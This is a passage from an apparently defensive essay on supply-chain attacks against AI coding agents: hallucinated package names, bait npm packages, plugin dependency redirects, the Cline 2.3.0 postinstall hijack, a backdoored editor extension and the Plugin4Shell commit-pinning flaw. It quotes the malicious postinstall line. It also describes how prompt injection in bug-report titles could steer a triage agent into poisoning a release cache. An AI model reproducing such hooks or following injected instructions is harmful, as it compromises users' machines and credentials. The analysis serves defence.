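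If the hosted version needs a key to use the mirror, the setup script runs too early to use a stored one. Anthropic can add a stored key to requests without revealing it to Claude, but only after Claude Code has started. An operator could write the key into the setup script, but everyone who uses the environment could then read it. It would be safer to install the packages from a start-up hook, a command that Claude Code runs at the beginning of a session, when the stored key should be available.

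## The package "react-codeshift" and agents that choose their own dependencies

A domain list or a mirror limits where an agent can get packages, but an agent that can reach a public registry still chooses which ones to request. It may request a package that does not exist. Anyone can then publish a package under that name, and the next agent to request it will install it.

In *Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands*, Eriksen describes registering `react-codeshift` on npm on 14 January 2026 for Aikido Security, a software security company. Nobody had ever published a package with that name, but 237 GitHub repositories already contained instructions for AI agents to run it.

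### From one commit to 237 repositories

Eriksen traced the name to a single commit of 17 October 2025 in a public collection of add-ons for coding agents. The commit added 47 skills that a language model had written, apparently without human review. At least two of them contained commands of this form:

```
npx react-codeshift --transform=<path of a code change> ./src
```

`npx` runs a program from an npm package and offers to download the package if the machine has no copy. Two real tools have names similar to "react-codeshift". Facebook's jscodeshift rewrites JavaScript code automatically, and react-codemod supplies ready-made rewrites for React, a library for building user interfaces. Eriksen concludes that the model merged the two names.

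Other users then copied the skills. About 100 of the repositories are forks that keep the file in its original place. One user copied it into more than 30 repositories, and someone translated it into Japanese. Another user replaced `npx` with `bunx`, a similar command that downloads from the same registry. None of the repositories was prominent, so the figure of 237 is better evidence of copying than of use.

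Eriksen's package, an empty placeholder, had about 74 downloads on its first day and then 4, 1, 3, 1 and 3 over the next five days. He writes that an unused npm package normally gets 60 to 100 downloads from mirrors and security scanners on its first day and none afterwards, so he attributes the later downloads to agents that were following the skills. That is plausible, but there were only twelve, and a download count doesn't show whether an agent, a person or another scanner downloaded the package.

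The command's effect could change without any change to the skill file. An auditor who tried the command in November 2025 would have seen an error, because npm had no such package. From 14 January, the same command could download and run whatever the name's owner published. Pinning the skill by hash would not have prevented this, nor would a domain allowlist that included npm. In a sealed image without network access, the command would still have failed. On a connected machine, `npx --no` refuses to download a missing package.

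Human authors make this mistake too. Eriksen writes in *npx Confusion* that he began looking for such names in July 2025, when he found instructions in a database library's documentation to run a package that nobody had published.

### Why models invent names and repeat them

A language model produces a package name piece by piece, choosing pieces that are likely in the context. It does not look the name up unless the harness lets it. Because package names follow conventions, a likely name may not belong to any existing package.

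Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, suggests two reasons why different models invent the same package names. Tutorials often refer to a package by something other than its registered name. For example, Python code imports pillow, the image package from the spreadsheet example, as `PIL`. Models may also apply a naming convention where it does not hold.

Slopsquatting means registering invented package names to attack the people who install them. *Slopsquatting meets Dependency Confusion* (2025) traces the word to an April 2025 conversation about registries' records of failed requests, which would show which missing packages people most often try to install.

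*We Have a Package for You!* (Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues, 2024), which appeared at the USENIX Security conference in 2025, was the first large study of the problem. The study used 576,000 Python and JavaScript code samples from 16 models. Some prompts were popular questions from the programming forum Stack Overflow, and a language model wrote the others from descriptions of widely downloaded packages. The researchers took package names from the install commands in the answers, and also asked each model which packages its code and the original task required.

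Of the 2.23 million packages that the 16 models named, 440,445 (19.7%) were missing from lists of every package on PyPI and npm in January 2024. These included 205,474 different names. The 13 open-source models averaged 21.7%, against 5.2% for the three commercial models. The 19.7% figure therefore mainly describes open models that are now more than two years old.

Spracklen and colleagues took 500 prompts that had produced an invented name and ran each one ten more times to see whether the errors were random. The same name came back in all ten runs for 43% of the prompts and in none for 39%. Restricting the models to their more likely choices of text did not reduce the rate of invented names, presumably because an invented name can itself be the most likely choice.

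Invented package names are useful to an attacker because they recur. If a name appears in a fraction p of the answers to a common question, an attacker who asks the question ten times will see the name at least once with probability 1 − (1 − p)¹⁰. If N users ask the same question, about pN of them will receive the name. When p is 0.01, the attacker has only about a 10% chance of finding the name and only one user in a hundred receives it, whereas when p is 1, the attacker and every user will see it.

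### Rates for newer models and for agents

Churilov put the same prompts to five newer models in April 2026 and collected 199,840 answers. In November he checked the package names against the live registries. The share of package mentions that were invented ranged from 3.63% for Claude Haiku 4.5 to 5.02% for GPT-5.4-mini. The only open model, DeepSeek V3.2, had a rate of 4.80%, so it no longer lagged far behind the commercial ones.

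Between 2.15% and 3.39% of each model's answers contained at least one invented name. The comparison with 2024 is approximate, because Churilov took names only from install commands and import statements and did not ask the models for lists. The prompts had also been public since January 2025, so they may have been in the models' training data, which could make the rates too low.

All five models invented 104 names in common. If the registry let an attacker take one of these names, a single malicious package could reach users of several companies' models. But packages appeared under only 25 of 2,282 invented names (1.1%) within about six months, and at least one of these packages contained malware. The models also suggested at least 23 names that had hosted malware before the registries removed it.

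Churilov had accidentally published his list of shared names in April, so he could test whether publication attracts attackers. One of the 104 names on the current list gained a package, compared with 24 of the 2,178 others, so there was no visible effect. The test could have detected only a large effect, such as a rise from 1% to about 10.5%.

Churilov excluded agents that can look packages up, so these rates do not apply to them. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) tested retrieval, which gives a model relevant reference material before it answers. The average rate for Python across eight models fell from 24.7% to 11.5%. Some of the models were very small, so the improvement is more informative than the rates. TrendAI's *Slopsquatting* concludes that checks against live package data reduce invented package names in coding agents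 such as Claude Code and Codex but do not eliminate them.

Some tasks can produce much higher rates of invented package names. Chen, of Tencent's Xuanwu Lab, asked a coding model for packages that would improve a website's appearance, and up to 40% of the names were invented. The lab registered an empty package under a name the model often invented. Within 20 days it had more than 500 downloads, not counting copies made by mirrors. Chen names neither the model nor the package, so outsiders can't repeat the test. The post also promotes Tencent's own protective plugin.

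A registry lookup shows only whether a package exists. Spracklen and colleagues point out that an attacker may already have published a package under the invented name. A lookup of `react-codeshift` has succeeded since the day Eriksen registered it.

### Packages with documentation that attracts models

Attackers can also publish a package and try to get agents to choose it. *Claude adds malware to crypto agent* (Pezo, 2026) describes a campaign that the security company ReversingLabs calls PromptMink. The attackers published bait packages for cryptocurrency developers, with some working functions and documentation that praised the packages highly. The bait packages contained no malicious code themselves, but they depended on many popular packages and a few malicious ones, which searched the user's machine for passwords and keys.

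On 28 February 2026, a commit co-authored by Anthropic's model Claude Opus brought the malware into `openpaw-graveyard`, an automated trading program. The program used the bait package `@solana-launchpad/sdk`, which required the malicious `@validate-sdk/v2`. The attackers could then access users' cryptocurrency wallets. The co-author line shows that Claude worked on the commit, but not whether Claude or a person chose the package.

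The attackers kept the bait and the malware in separate packages, which helped them survive detection. When npm removed an earlier malicious package on 7 October 2025, the attackers published the same code as `@validate-sdk/v2` that day and updated the bait to use it, so the bait kept its name and reputation. ReversingLabs found 60 packages and more than 300 versions over seven months, and attributes them to the North Korean group Famous Chollima.

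Pezo believes AI agents may have been the main target, since attackers can test their documentation on a model before publishing it. He found two users of the bait, and both cases involved an AI agent. But two cases are a small sample, and human developers read the same documentation. A check for invented names would have accepted every package, because they all existed.

### A plugin that replaces the real package

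An agent may also ask for the right package and receive an altered copy. In *When Your Plugin Starts Picking Your Dependencies*, Abutbul (2026) demonstrates this with Claude Code and a plugin from an unofficial marketplace. According to its description, the plugin keeps Python packages pinned and secure. When the developer asks for httpx, a real library for web requests, Claude uses the plugin's skill, which installs a malicious version from the attacker's server.

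The import works, the example code runs, and the skill changes the project's requirements so that the malicious version stays. The main visible clue is an unfamiliar package address in the output. SentinelOne's *When Your AI Coding Plugin Starts Picking Your Dependencies* notes that the skill remains available in later sessions, so it can also redirect future installations. SentinelOne, which sells protection against such attacks, staged this demonstration and reported no victims.

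Other research suggests that agents would often miss the clue. *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* (2026) tested nine combinations of harness and model on projects with manipulated setup instructions. The agents noticed bad package names far more often than bad sources, and installed from untrusted registries almost every time. A strict domain list would block the download in Abutbul's demonstration unless the attacker used a permitted host, but it would not stop a skill from steering the agent to a harmful package on PyPI or npm. *Trust Me, Import This* (2026) shows that skills can influence an agent's choice of package like this.

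### An approval procedure for new packages

An operator can let agents propose packages without letting them install any. Suppose the finance manager wants PDF reports, and the spreadsheet agent proposes the package reportlab. The container has no network connection, so the agent submits a request through a tool that the harness provides:

```
{
  "package": "reportlab",
  "version": "<exact version>",
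  "reason": "PDF output for the monthly sales report",
  "suggested_by": "model"
}
```

If the suggestion came from a skill or web page, the last field would name it. The agent may get this wrong, so the reviewer should compare the field with the harness's log.

A program that the agent cannot alter then checks the name. If the operator has already approved this version, the request needs no further review. Otherwise the program looks the package up on PyPI and rejects the request if it isn't there. The program should always use the operator's chosen registry and ignore any source named in the project. This would defeat the redirect in Abutbul's demonstration.

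*YUL* (2026) places a similar lookup in the harness. Whatever the model produces, the harness blocks an invented package before the agent's change to the project's dependency list is written to disk. A check limited to that list would miss `npx react-codeshift`, which can run without being listed, so the check also has to cover commands that download and run packages, such as `npx` and `bunx`.

The program next checks the package's age. *Importing Phantoms* (2025) counts a package as invented if it was first registered after the model's knowledge cutoff, the date its training data ends. The model could not have learned about such a package in training, so a reviewer should find out where the name came from. Useful new packages would also fail this test, so it works better as a warning than a ban. A minimum age alone is easy to satisfy. Both PromptMink packages in the trading program were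 more than four months old when the commit added them, so a 90-day minimum would have let them through.

The program also compares the hash of every file with the approved set, so the altered copy of httpx fails even if httpx is approved. The approved hashes must be stored outside the project, because a malicious plugin could write the altered file's hash into the project's own lockfile. The same comparison keeps out a hijacked new release of an approved package until someone reviews it.

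A new package has no approved hash, so a person has to decide whether to allow it. The reviewer should see reportlab and every package it would add. In the PromptMink case, a reviewer who examined only the bait package would have found nothing malicious, but checking its dependencies might have revealed that `@validate-sdk/v2`, supposedly a small validation tool, grew from 5.1 KB to about 85 MB in February 2026, when the attackers hid their code in a large executable. They later switched to smaller compiled files, which were harder to notice.

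If the reviewer approves, the operator adds reportlab to `requirements.in`, generates a new lockfile, rebuilds the image offline and signs the new digest. The agent then continues in a container started from the new image. The table shows how each check would affect the three kinds of attack.

| Check | Invented name | Bait package | Altered copy of a real package | Delay |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Registry lookup | Stops it only if nobody has registered the name | Lets it through | Lets it through, because the name is real | Probably seconds |
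| Package age | Flags recent registrations | Would miss PromptMink with a 90-day minimum | Lets it through, because the real package is old | None as a warning; up to the full period as a ban |
| Approved hashes | Holds it for review | Holds it for review | Stops it if the real version is approved | Probably seconds |
| Human review | Can stop it if the reviewer questions the name's origin | Can stop it if the reviewer examines every dependency | Can stop it if the reviewer uses the official file | Depends on staff |
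| Rebuilt image | Keeps out anything unapproved | Keeps out anything unapproved | Keeps out anything unapproved | Build and restart time |

### How often agents would have to wait

There appear to be no published measurements of how long such approvals take, but one study suggests how often agents would need them. Twist and Zhang (2025), in *A Study of Library Usage in Agent-Authored Pull Requests*, examined 26,760 code changes proposed by agents. Only 1.3%, or about 350, added a new dependency. At that rate, a team would review about 13 requests for every 1,000 changes. If each review took a working day, only those 13 changes would be delayed, each by a day.

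The real number would probably be higher, because the study counted only dependencies that remained in the proposed code. An agent may install a test tool or run something through `npx` without it appearing in the final changes. A quarter of the changes that added a dependency did not specify a version, so the operator would have to choose one before the review.

Chen's plugin avoids some of the waiting by correcting problems automatically. Before the agent installs a package or writes a dependency file, the plugin can replace an invented name with a real one, or a vulnerable version with a patched one, without notifying the user. This is convenient for ordinary development, but on an audited system it would introduce a package that nobody had approved. The auditors would also have to examine the plugin's database.

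An agent that keeps working after a refusal could write an imitation of the package that passes the tests but lacks the real functions. *Dependency Fabrication in Repository Deployment Agents* (2026) studies agents in a similar position, on projects that need a package they cannot legitimately obtain, for example because it is on a private server and they have no credentials. The operator can have the harness pause the task until the reviewer decides. After a refusal, the reviewer should check the agent's changes for such an imitation, because it would contain code that the approval procedure never examined.

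## Cline 2.3.0 and the choice between pinning and updating

An approval procedure also has to cover new versions of software the operator has already approved, including the harness. An operator who installs every version on the day it appears will sometimes install a malicious one. Staying on an old version avoids those releases but keeps every flaw that researchers later find in it.

### Eight hours on npm

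Cline is an open-source coding agent that developers can install as an editor extension or, from npm, as a command-line program. At 3:26 a.m. Pacific time on 17 February 2026, an unknown person published version 2.3.0 of the command-line program using a stolen npm token, a key that lets its holder upload new versions. According to the maintainers' advisory, reproduced in OSV's *GHSA-9ppg-jx86-fqw7* (2026), the attacker changed only `package.json`, the file that describes the package, and added this line:

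```
"postinstall": "npm install -g openclaw@latest"
```

npm normally runs a package's `postinstall` command as soon as it has installed the package. This command installed a second agent, OpenClaw, which people run on their own machines. The maintainers released a clean version, 2.4.0, at 11:23 a.m. and marked 2.3.0 as deprecated seven minutes later, about eight hours after it appeared.

The Hacker News, citing the security company StepSecurity, reports roughly 4,000 downloads in that time. Mirrors and scanners also download packages, so fewer than 4,000 machines may have received OpenClaw. Microsoft saw a "small but noticeable uptick" in OpenClaw installations that day. The harm was low because OpenClaw is a legitimate project and the command did not start its background service. The attacker could have used the same line to run a program that steals passwords.

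An auditor who checked only the main program file would have missed the change. *Post-mortem*, Cline's account of the incident (Rizwan, 2026), confirms that this file had the same SHA-256 hash as in version 2.2.3, so it would have matched the approved set A. The guarantee failed because of OpenClaw, whose files were not in A.

### Who was protected by a lockfile

A lockfile helped only people whose install command used it. Developers usually install a command-line agent globally, for use in any folder, and npm ignores project lockfiles when it does that. Under npm's normal rules, the outcomes during those eight hours would have been as follows:

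| What the operator did | Result |
|---|---|
| Ran `npm ci` with an earlier lockfile that included Cline | The locked version, without OpenClaw |
| Ran `npm install -g cline@2.2.3` | Version 2.2.3, without OpenClaw |
| Ran `npm install -g cline` | Version 2.3.0 and OpenClaw |
| Ran the same command with `--ignore-scripts` | Version 2.3.0, without OpenClaw |
| Created a new lockfile that included Cline | A lockfile that names 2.3.0 |
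| Started a sealed image built earlier | The version in the image, without OpenClaw |

The new lockfile could have kept adding OpenClaw at each installation long after the incident, as long as 2.3.0 stayed on the registry. It would have recorded a correct hash for the unauthorised release, and npm still delivers deprecated versions, with a warning. The lockfile would not have pinned OpenClaw's own version, because the command added in 2.3.0 always requested the latest one.

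### The agent that sorted bug reports

The theft of the token began with a different AI agent. In December 2025, Cline's maintainers set up Claude to sort incoming bug reports on GitHub and let it run shell commands. Rizwan explains that anyone with a GitHub account could put instructions in a report's title, and Claude might follow them. The sorting job could not change Cline's code, but it shared a file cache with the job that published Cline's nightly releases.

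An attacker could therefore have had Claude fill the cache with more than 10 GB of junk, which makes GitHub delete older entries. The attacker could then have stored altered files under the names the release job looked for. When the release job loaded them, the attacker's code would have run with access to the publishing tokens.

The security researcher Adnan Khan reported this weakness on 1 January 2026, but the maintainers did not act until he made it public on 9 February. They removed the sorting job within 30 minutes and began to replace their tokens, but they deleted the wrong npm token. npm's management page then showed no active tokens, although the exposed one still worked, and someone used it eight days later. Cline now tests whether an old token has stopped working instead of relying on the page.

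Cline has also stopped using stored tokens for npm. It now uses trusted publishing, in which npm verifies the identity of GitHub's build service for each release, and each version has a signed record of its source commit and build job. Cline apparently had such a process before the attack, but *supply chain attack targeting cline installs openclaw* (Plate, 2026) concludes that the attacker bypassed it with a long-lived token. Plate advises users to watch for packages whose signed records suddenly disappear.

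Adebayo (2026) reports in *How AI coding tools could amplify software supply-chain attacks* that the company Bloom Security found a flaw in trusted publishing itself. npm identified a trusted GitHub repository by its name instead of its permanent number, so someone who took over an abandoned name could presumably have published as its former owner. Bloom counted more than 1,500 vulnerable packages, and GitHub fixed the flaw on 2 October 2026, almost four months after Bloom's report. The records also would not have exposed the cache attack, because a release built from altered cache files would still have come from the correct commit and build job.

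### A tampered extension with a genuine version number

In October 2026, an attacker tampered with the Claude Code extension in the marketplace of Cursor, the coding agent and editor. According to Cursor's *Security notice*, the exposure lasted about 11 hours, from about 2:27 a.m. to 1:35 p.m. Pacific time on 29 October, and affected 5,000 or fewer users.

The extension's code ran as soon as the editor loaded it. It tried to set up SSH, a standard system for logging in to another computer, so that the attacker could connect to the user's machine. It also sent the attacker the user's name, Git email address and other details. Help Net Security's *Claude Code extension poisoned with persistent SSH backdoor* (2026) adds that the other details included the names, but not the values, of up to 40 environment variables that looked like passwords or keys. On most Mac and Windows machines, the step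 that turned on SSH would have failed because it lacked administrator rights. Scripts the extension left behind could keep running after it was removed.

Early reports disagreed about where the malicious file had been. Help Net Security placed it on Open VSX, a public marketplace from which Cursor gets extensions. After two weeks of investigation, Cursor's *An update on our recent security incident* stated that the file had never been on Open VSX. The attacker had used a stolen credential to put altered copies of versions 2.1.312 and 2.1.313 directly on the cache that supplies Cursor's marketplace. Cursor's first notice had mentioned only 2.1.313, so anyone who relied on it could have missed 2.1.312.

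Pinning the version number would not have protected users here, because the cache could still have supplied the altered copy even if an operator had told the editor to install exactly 2.1.312. Checking the publisher's name would not have helped either, since the marketplace listing was Anthropic's real one. The altered copy's hash would have differed from one taken earlier from a genuine copy, but something would have had to compare the two before the editor loaded the extension.

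Cursor traces the attack to an access key that leaked from Fireworks, a company it used for training and running models. The key opened a store of records from coding agents' sessions, a few of which contained unredacted credentials. From there the attacker reached other internal tools and found more credentials. Operators who keep agents' commands for later audits therefore need to remove passwords and keys from them.

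### The case for waiting

Most people who avoided Cline 2.3.0 did so because they happened not to update that morning. A dependency cooldown makes that delay deliberate by having the package manager refuse any release younger than a set age, such as seven days. The developer William Woodruff argued for the practice in November 2025. Of ten earlier attacks he examined, eight had lasted less than a week. These were prominent cases that people had noticed, so the share for all attacks may be lower.

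*We should all be using dependency cooldowns* (Willison, 2025) explains that cooldowns work because an attacker who takes over a popular package often has only a few hours before someone spots the malicious release. In 2026, attackers compromised Axios, a JavaScript library with about 100 million downloads a week. They added a malicious dependency that they had published only minutes before, according to issue *#322* of the security newsletter tl;dr sec. A one-day cooldown would have blocked both packages that day.

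Nesbitt (2026), in *package managers need to cool down*, surveyed support for cooldowns at the request of Seth Larson, who wants every tool to accept one general setting such as "7d". A list that Willison published the same month includes these tools:

| Tool | Language | First version with support | Setting |
|---|---|---|---|
| Bun | JavaScript | 1.3, October 2025 | `minimumReleaseAge` |
| Deno | JavaScript | 2.6, December 2025 | `--minimum-dependency-age` |
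| uv | Python | 0.9.17, December 2025 | `--exclude-newer` with a relative age |
| pip | Python | 26.0, January 2026; relative ages from 26.1, April 2026 | `--uploaded-prior-to` |
| npm | JavaScript | 11.10.0, February 2026 | `min-release-age` |

Waiting helps only if someone withdraws the bad release in time. Under a one-day rule, Cline 2.3.0 would have become old enough to install at 3:26 a.m. on 18 February, and the clean 2.4.0 would have followed at 11:23. For the eight hours between, the newest permitted version would have been the unauthorised one. Cline had deprecated it but not removed it, so whether it was installed would have depended on whether the package manager skips deprecated versions. A seven-day rule would have had the same gap on 24 February.

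Cooldowns also depend on accurate release dates. The attacker in the Cursor incident replaced files under existing version numbers, so a tool that checked only the original publication date would have treated the new files as old. Cooldowns don't stop malicious packages that have gone undetected for months, as in the PromptMink campaign.

### Who installs first

Paterson, in *Dependency cooldowns turn you into a free-rider*, objects that people who use cooldowns rely on others being attacked first. Users without a cooldown install the new release, are attacked and raise the alarm, and everyone else benefits. If all users waited a week, nobody would discover the problem in that time, and the attack would begin a week later.

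That assumes only victims discover attacks, but companies also scan new packages automatically, and GitHub scans all of the more than 30,000 package versions published on npm each day. In the forum discussion *Dependency cooldowns are unfair; we should use phased rollouts instead*, one participant replies that the delay mainly gives maintainers time to notice a stolen account. Khan first reported Cline 2.3.0, and Endor Labs' monitoring of new packages also detected it, so its discovery didn't depend on thousands of victims.

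Scanners can miss some attacks, though. An instruction to install a popular, legitimate agent looks much less suspicious than code that steals passwords. Some malicious code, like the library that NVIDIA tested on Codex, also stays inactive until it runs in a particular environment. Paterson's objection still applies to such code, because someone may have to run it before anyone sees what it does.

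One participant in the forum discussion proposes phased rollouts as a fairer alternative. A registry would offer a new release to a small share of users first and to more over time, so the risk would no longer fall on those who had never heard of cooldowns. Another participant imagines a registry that shows new releases only to security scanners until their checks are finished. Either system would need the registry's cooperation, whereas an operator can set a cooldown alone.

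### The case for updating

If researchers find a vulnerability in a sealed image's software after the audit, it stays in the image until someone rebuilds it. According to tl;dr sec's summary of GitHub's figures for 2025, GitHub's notices about malicious packages rose by 69% to 7,197, which is a reason to wait before updating, while newly reported vulnerabilities rose by 19%, which is a reason to update quickly.

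GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Cline package* lists a flaw in kanban, a package that Cline's command-line program uses. Kanban starts a server on the developer's machine that accepts connections from any website the developer visits. A malicious site could read the agent's messages or send it instructions, and use those instructions to run commands. An operator who froze a version with this flaw would keep the flaw, no matter how carefully the auditors had checked the hashes.

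Sometimes an operator has a good reason to stay on an old version. *SCARVA* (Barsch, Nogueira et al., 2026) tested how well AI agents judge whether a vulnerable library endangers the program that uses it. The study used Codex 0.116.0 because later versions had a bug. OpenAI did not fix Plugin4Shell, a flaw in how Codex handles plugins, until version 0.146.0. Avoiding one bug can therefore mean keeping another, although the version number alone does not show that the study was exposed, since an attacker would also have needed a way to exploit the plugin feature.

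Not every flaw in an old image matters. Barsch and colleagues call a program affected only if an attacker can get input to the vulnerable code and the program is in a state that triggers the flaw. The web server nginx 1.4.7 used a release of OpenSSL with the Heartbleed flaw, and anyone who could open an encrypted connection could exploit it. The database MongoDB 8.2.6 contains a vulnerable release of the compression library Brotli, but by default it never uses Brotli for network messages. An SBOM scanner would flag both programs, although only nginx needs an urgent update.

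Agents are not yet reliable at making this distinction. On 54 cases, the models working alone scored between 0.556 and 0.667 in balanced accuracy, which gives each kind of case equal weight. The best score rose to 0.819 when a panel of four other agents checked the first agent's claims against a record of its actions. Many agents hedged or reported a vulnerability where the library had none. All the cases involve known flaws in C and C++ libraries, so results for Python packages could differ. For now, a person should confirm an agent's conclusion that an old image is safe to keep.

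### The trade-off as a formula

Let d be the number of days between a release and its installation. The expected number of security incidents per year is then roughly

R(d) = m · S(d) + u · (1 − (1 − q)ᵈ)

Here m is the number of malicious releases per year among the packages in the image, and S(d) is the share of those releases not yet withdrawn after d days. New releases fix u flaws per year that an attacker could reach, and q is the daily chance that someone exploits one of them before the operator installs the fix. The first term falls as d grows, and the second rises. The formula leaves out flaws that have no fix yet, because waiting makes no difference to them.

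Suppose a connected coding agent has m = 0.5, u = 6 and q = 0.1%. These numbers and the values of S(d) are invented, except for the 20% at seven days, which matches Woodruff's count.

| Delay d | S(d) | Malicious releases | Unpatched flaws | Total R(d) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0 days | 100% | 0.500 | 0.000 | 0.500 |
| 1 day | 30% | 0.150 | 0.006 | 0.156 |
| 7 days | 20% | 0.100 | 0.042 | 0.142 |
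| 14 days | 10% | 0.050 | 0.083 | 0.133 |
| 30 days | 10% | 0.050 | 0.177 | 0.227 |
| 90 days | 5% | 0.025 | 0.517 | 0.542 |

With these numbers, two weeks is the best of the six delays, but one day is nearly as good because most of the benefit comes from not updating immediately. A 90-day delay is worse than no delay because of the unpatched flaws.

The result depends on the agent's surroundings, because an attacker can reach fewer flaws in a container without a network. If u falls from 6 to 1 and the other values stay the same, the total at 90 days is only 0.111, so the operator of the spreadsheet agent could reasonably rebuild the image less often. The formula also counts all incidents as equally serious. An operator who considers a malicious release ten times as harmful as an exploited flaw can multiply the first term by ten, which favours a longer wait.

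A sealed image receives a new release only at the first rebuild after the cooldown ends. If the operator rebuilds every 30 days and uses a seven-day cooldown, a release waits 7 to 37 days, or 22 on average. Shortening the cooldown to one day would reduce the average to 16 days, while keeping the seven-day cooldown and rebuilding weekly would reduce it to 10.5.

Applying the same delay to every release is a poor rule when attackers are already exploiting a flaw. Suppose the daily chance of an attack is 5%. After a week without the fix, the chance of at least one attack is 1 − 0.95⁷, or about 30%. If the packages in the image have 300 releases a year, of which 0.5 on average are malicious, the chance that the fix is malicious is one in 600, and waiting a week would remove about four-fifths of that risk. The operator should install the fix at once. uv supports this with `exclude-newer-package`,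 which sets a different limit for a single package.

A reviewer can reduce the first term without waiting by comparing the new version with the old one. For Cline 2.3.0, that comparison would have shown only a new version number and the command that installed OpenClaw. Most updates are much larger, and Bloom Security, which sells protection for agents, reports that agents install close to 350 packages a month on some developers' machines. A person can't read everything at that rate, so the operator needs an automatic delay for ordinary releases and a quick review for urgent ones.

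### When an update voids an audit

An updated program file is outside A until the auditors approve it. Their findings still hold for unchanged files, but someone has to decide how much of the examination to repeat. Two bodies of law deal with a similar question for products that a regulator or assessor has already checked.

Under Article 43 of the EU AI Act, a high-risk system that undergoes a "substantial modification" needs a new conformity assessment, which checks it against the Act's requirements. A substantial modification is a change after the system goes on sale or into use that the provider did not plan for in the original assessment, and that either affects the system's compliance with those requirements or alters its intended purpose. High-risk uses include recruitment and credit scoring. Most coding agents fall outside the category, and the duties for high-risk systems have yet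 to take effect.

For an agent that ranks job applicants, a security fix to its image library probably wouldn't affect compliance with the Act. A new model that ranked applicants differently could affect compliance with the Act's accuracy requirement, so the agent might need a new assessment unless the provider had planned for the change. The Act's introductory text also mentions a new operating system as a possible reason for a new assessment. If the provider began to offer the agent for choosing whom to dismiss, it could need an assessment for that new purpose even if no hash had changed.

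The US Food and Drug Administration (FDA) lets manufacturers of medical devices agree on updates in advance through a predetermined change control plan. The plan describes the intended changes, how they will be made and tested, and their likely risks. If the FDA approves the plan with the device, changes that follow it need no new application. A company whose software finds tumours in scans could plan to retrain it on images from more hospitals, provided each new version still finds a stated share of the tumours. Any other significant change would need a new application, though the FDA's guidance on software changes generally exempts updates that only strengthen security.

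Neither law settles whether a private audit of a spreadsheet or coding agent still holds after an update. An operator and an auditor can settle it themselves by attaching a similar plan to the audit. For the spreadsheet agent, it might contain these rules:

| Change | What the auditors do before the new version goes into use |
|---|---|
| Security fix to an approved package | Compare the two versions and run the agent's tests |
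| New package | Follow the full approval procedure |
| New harness version | Compare the two versions, then test the isolation and the list of tools again |
| New base image | Compare the package lists and rebuild the image on a second machine |
| New model or new purpose | Repeat the audit |

Each accepted change adds its files' hashes to A. The operator should remove the old hashes at the same time so that the vulnerable version can no longer run.

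## Plugin4Shell, a pinned version that was never checked

A plan for updates is useful only if the agent installs the version that the auditors approved. In September 2026, the security company AIR disclosed that four widely used coding agents (Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Google's Gemini CLI) requested the approved version of a plugin but never confirmed that they had received it. AIR named the flaw Plugin4Shell.

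A swapped plugin can do a lot of damage because it has the same access to the machine as the person who runs the agent. In an August 2026 guide, the software company Red Hat notes that a Claude Code plugin can include shell commands that run at the start of every session, before the user has typed anything.

### How a marketplace pins a plugin

A plugin marketplace is a catalogue whose entries typically give a plugin's name and the address of the Git repository that holds its files. The agent downloads the files from that repository. The repository belongs to the plugin's author, who can change it at any time, including after a review.

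To hold the plugin at the reviewed version, the marketplace can add a commit identifier to the entry. Git computes this 40-character identifier from the files themselves. With H for the hash function, and leaving subfolders aside,

tree ID = H(file names and file hashes)

commit ID = H(tree ID, previous commit, author, date, message).

As with an image's digest, a change to any file therefore changes the identifier.

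Suppose a company uses a plugin called `release-notes`, which drafts announcements of new software versions. The marketplace's reviewers read version 1.4 and record its commit in the plugin's entry. If the author, or a thief who has taken over the author's account, later adds a script that copies passwords, users should still receive the reviewed files, because the script belongs to a different commit. When the author submits version 1.5, the reviewers read it and put its commit in the entry. AIR's *Plugin4Shell* sums up what users expect: "the pinned commit is what runs forever after".

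### The missing comparison

The agents gave Git the commit identifier and assumed that Git would retrieve the right files. But Git also lets developers name branches, or parallel lines of work, almost anything, including a string that looks like a commit identifier. Constantin (2026) explains in *Plugin4Shell* that someone who controlled a plugin's repository could use this ambiguity to deliver different code. The agent would still report a clean installation at the pinned commit. Gemini CLI had a related fault. It fetched the correct commit, but a second ambiguous name could make it write other files to disk.

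Git's protection against damaged files would not have helped, because the files were intact and matched the hashes of a real commit. The reviewers had read a different commit.

The fix is one comparison. After the download, the agent asks Git which commit the files in the folder come from, and stops if the answer differs from the pin. In a shell script, it could look like this:

```
test "$(git rev-parse HEAD)" = "$PIN" || exit 1
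```

`HEAD` is Git's name for the commit that is currently checked out, and `$PIN` holds the identifier from the marketplace. The check has to happen before the agent runs anything from the plugin. It works against both faults because it compares the commit that was actually checked out with the pin. An ambiguous name could still make Git produce the wrong files, but the agent would refuse to load them. pip's strict mode applies the same principle to Python packages.

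Recording a version and verifying it are therefore separate steps, and the four agents did only the first. The same mistake is easy to make in an audit log. If the harness logs "release-notes, commit 3f9a…" because it requested that commit, an investigator will later see the correct pin even if the plugin ran other code. A useful start-up record contains a value computed from the installed files.

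### How updates reached installed plugins

AIR describes Plugin4Shell as a zero-click remote code execution (RCE) flaw, meaning an attacker can run programs on someone else's machine without any action by that person. The victim does need to have the plugin already or install it, but after that an automatic update is enough.

Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* reports AIR's explanation that a background update repeats the same unchecked download whenever the marketplace changes the pin. In the example, the reviewers approve version 1.5 of `release-notes` and record its commit. Overnight, every agent with the plugin requests that commit and could receive files that no reviewer has seen, even though the company's developers and reviewers have done nothing wrong.

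AIR also states that background updates are the default in Claude Code and Codex. This is somewhat too broad for Claude Code, where background updates from third-party marketplaces are off by default. A user who kept that setting would still have been exposed when installing a plugin from one of those marketplaces or updating it by hand. Turning background updates off everywhere would not have protected an operator who installs the plugins in a fresh container for each task, because each task would begin with a new unchecked download.

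The attack also depends on where the plugin's repository is hosted. GitHub rejects branch names that look like full commit identifiers, but Bitbucket and Git servers that companies run themselves allow them. For Claude Code, Codex and Copilot, a plugin hosted on GitHub was therefore safe from this trick. AIR claims in its headline that the flaw affected "millions of agents", which seems to count everyone who uses the four products. The number who had a plugin from a host that allows such names must be smaller, possibly much smaller. Help Net Security mentions AIR's working exploits but no attack on real users.

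A marketplace could accept only plugins hosted on GitHub. AIR objects that this would exclude hosts that the agents officially support and would not fix Gemini CLI's version of the fault. The agent downloads the plugin, so the agent has to check it.

### What the vendors did

AIR found the flaw in May 2026 and told the four vendors in June. By the time it published the details on 17 September, two of them had released a fix.

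| Agent | Vendor's response by September 2026 | What users can do |
|---|---|---|
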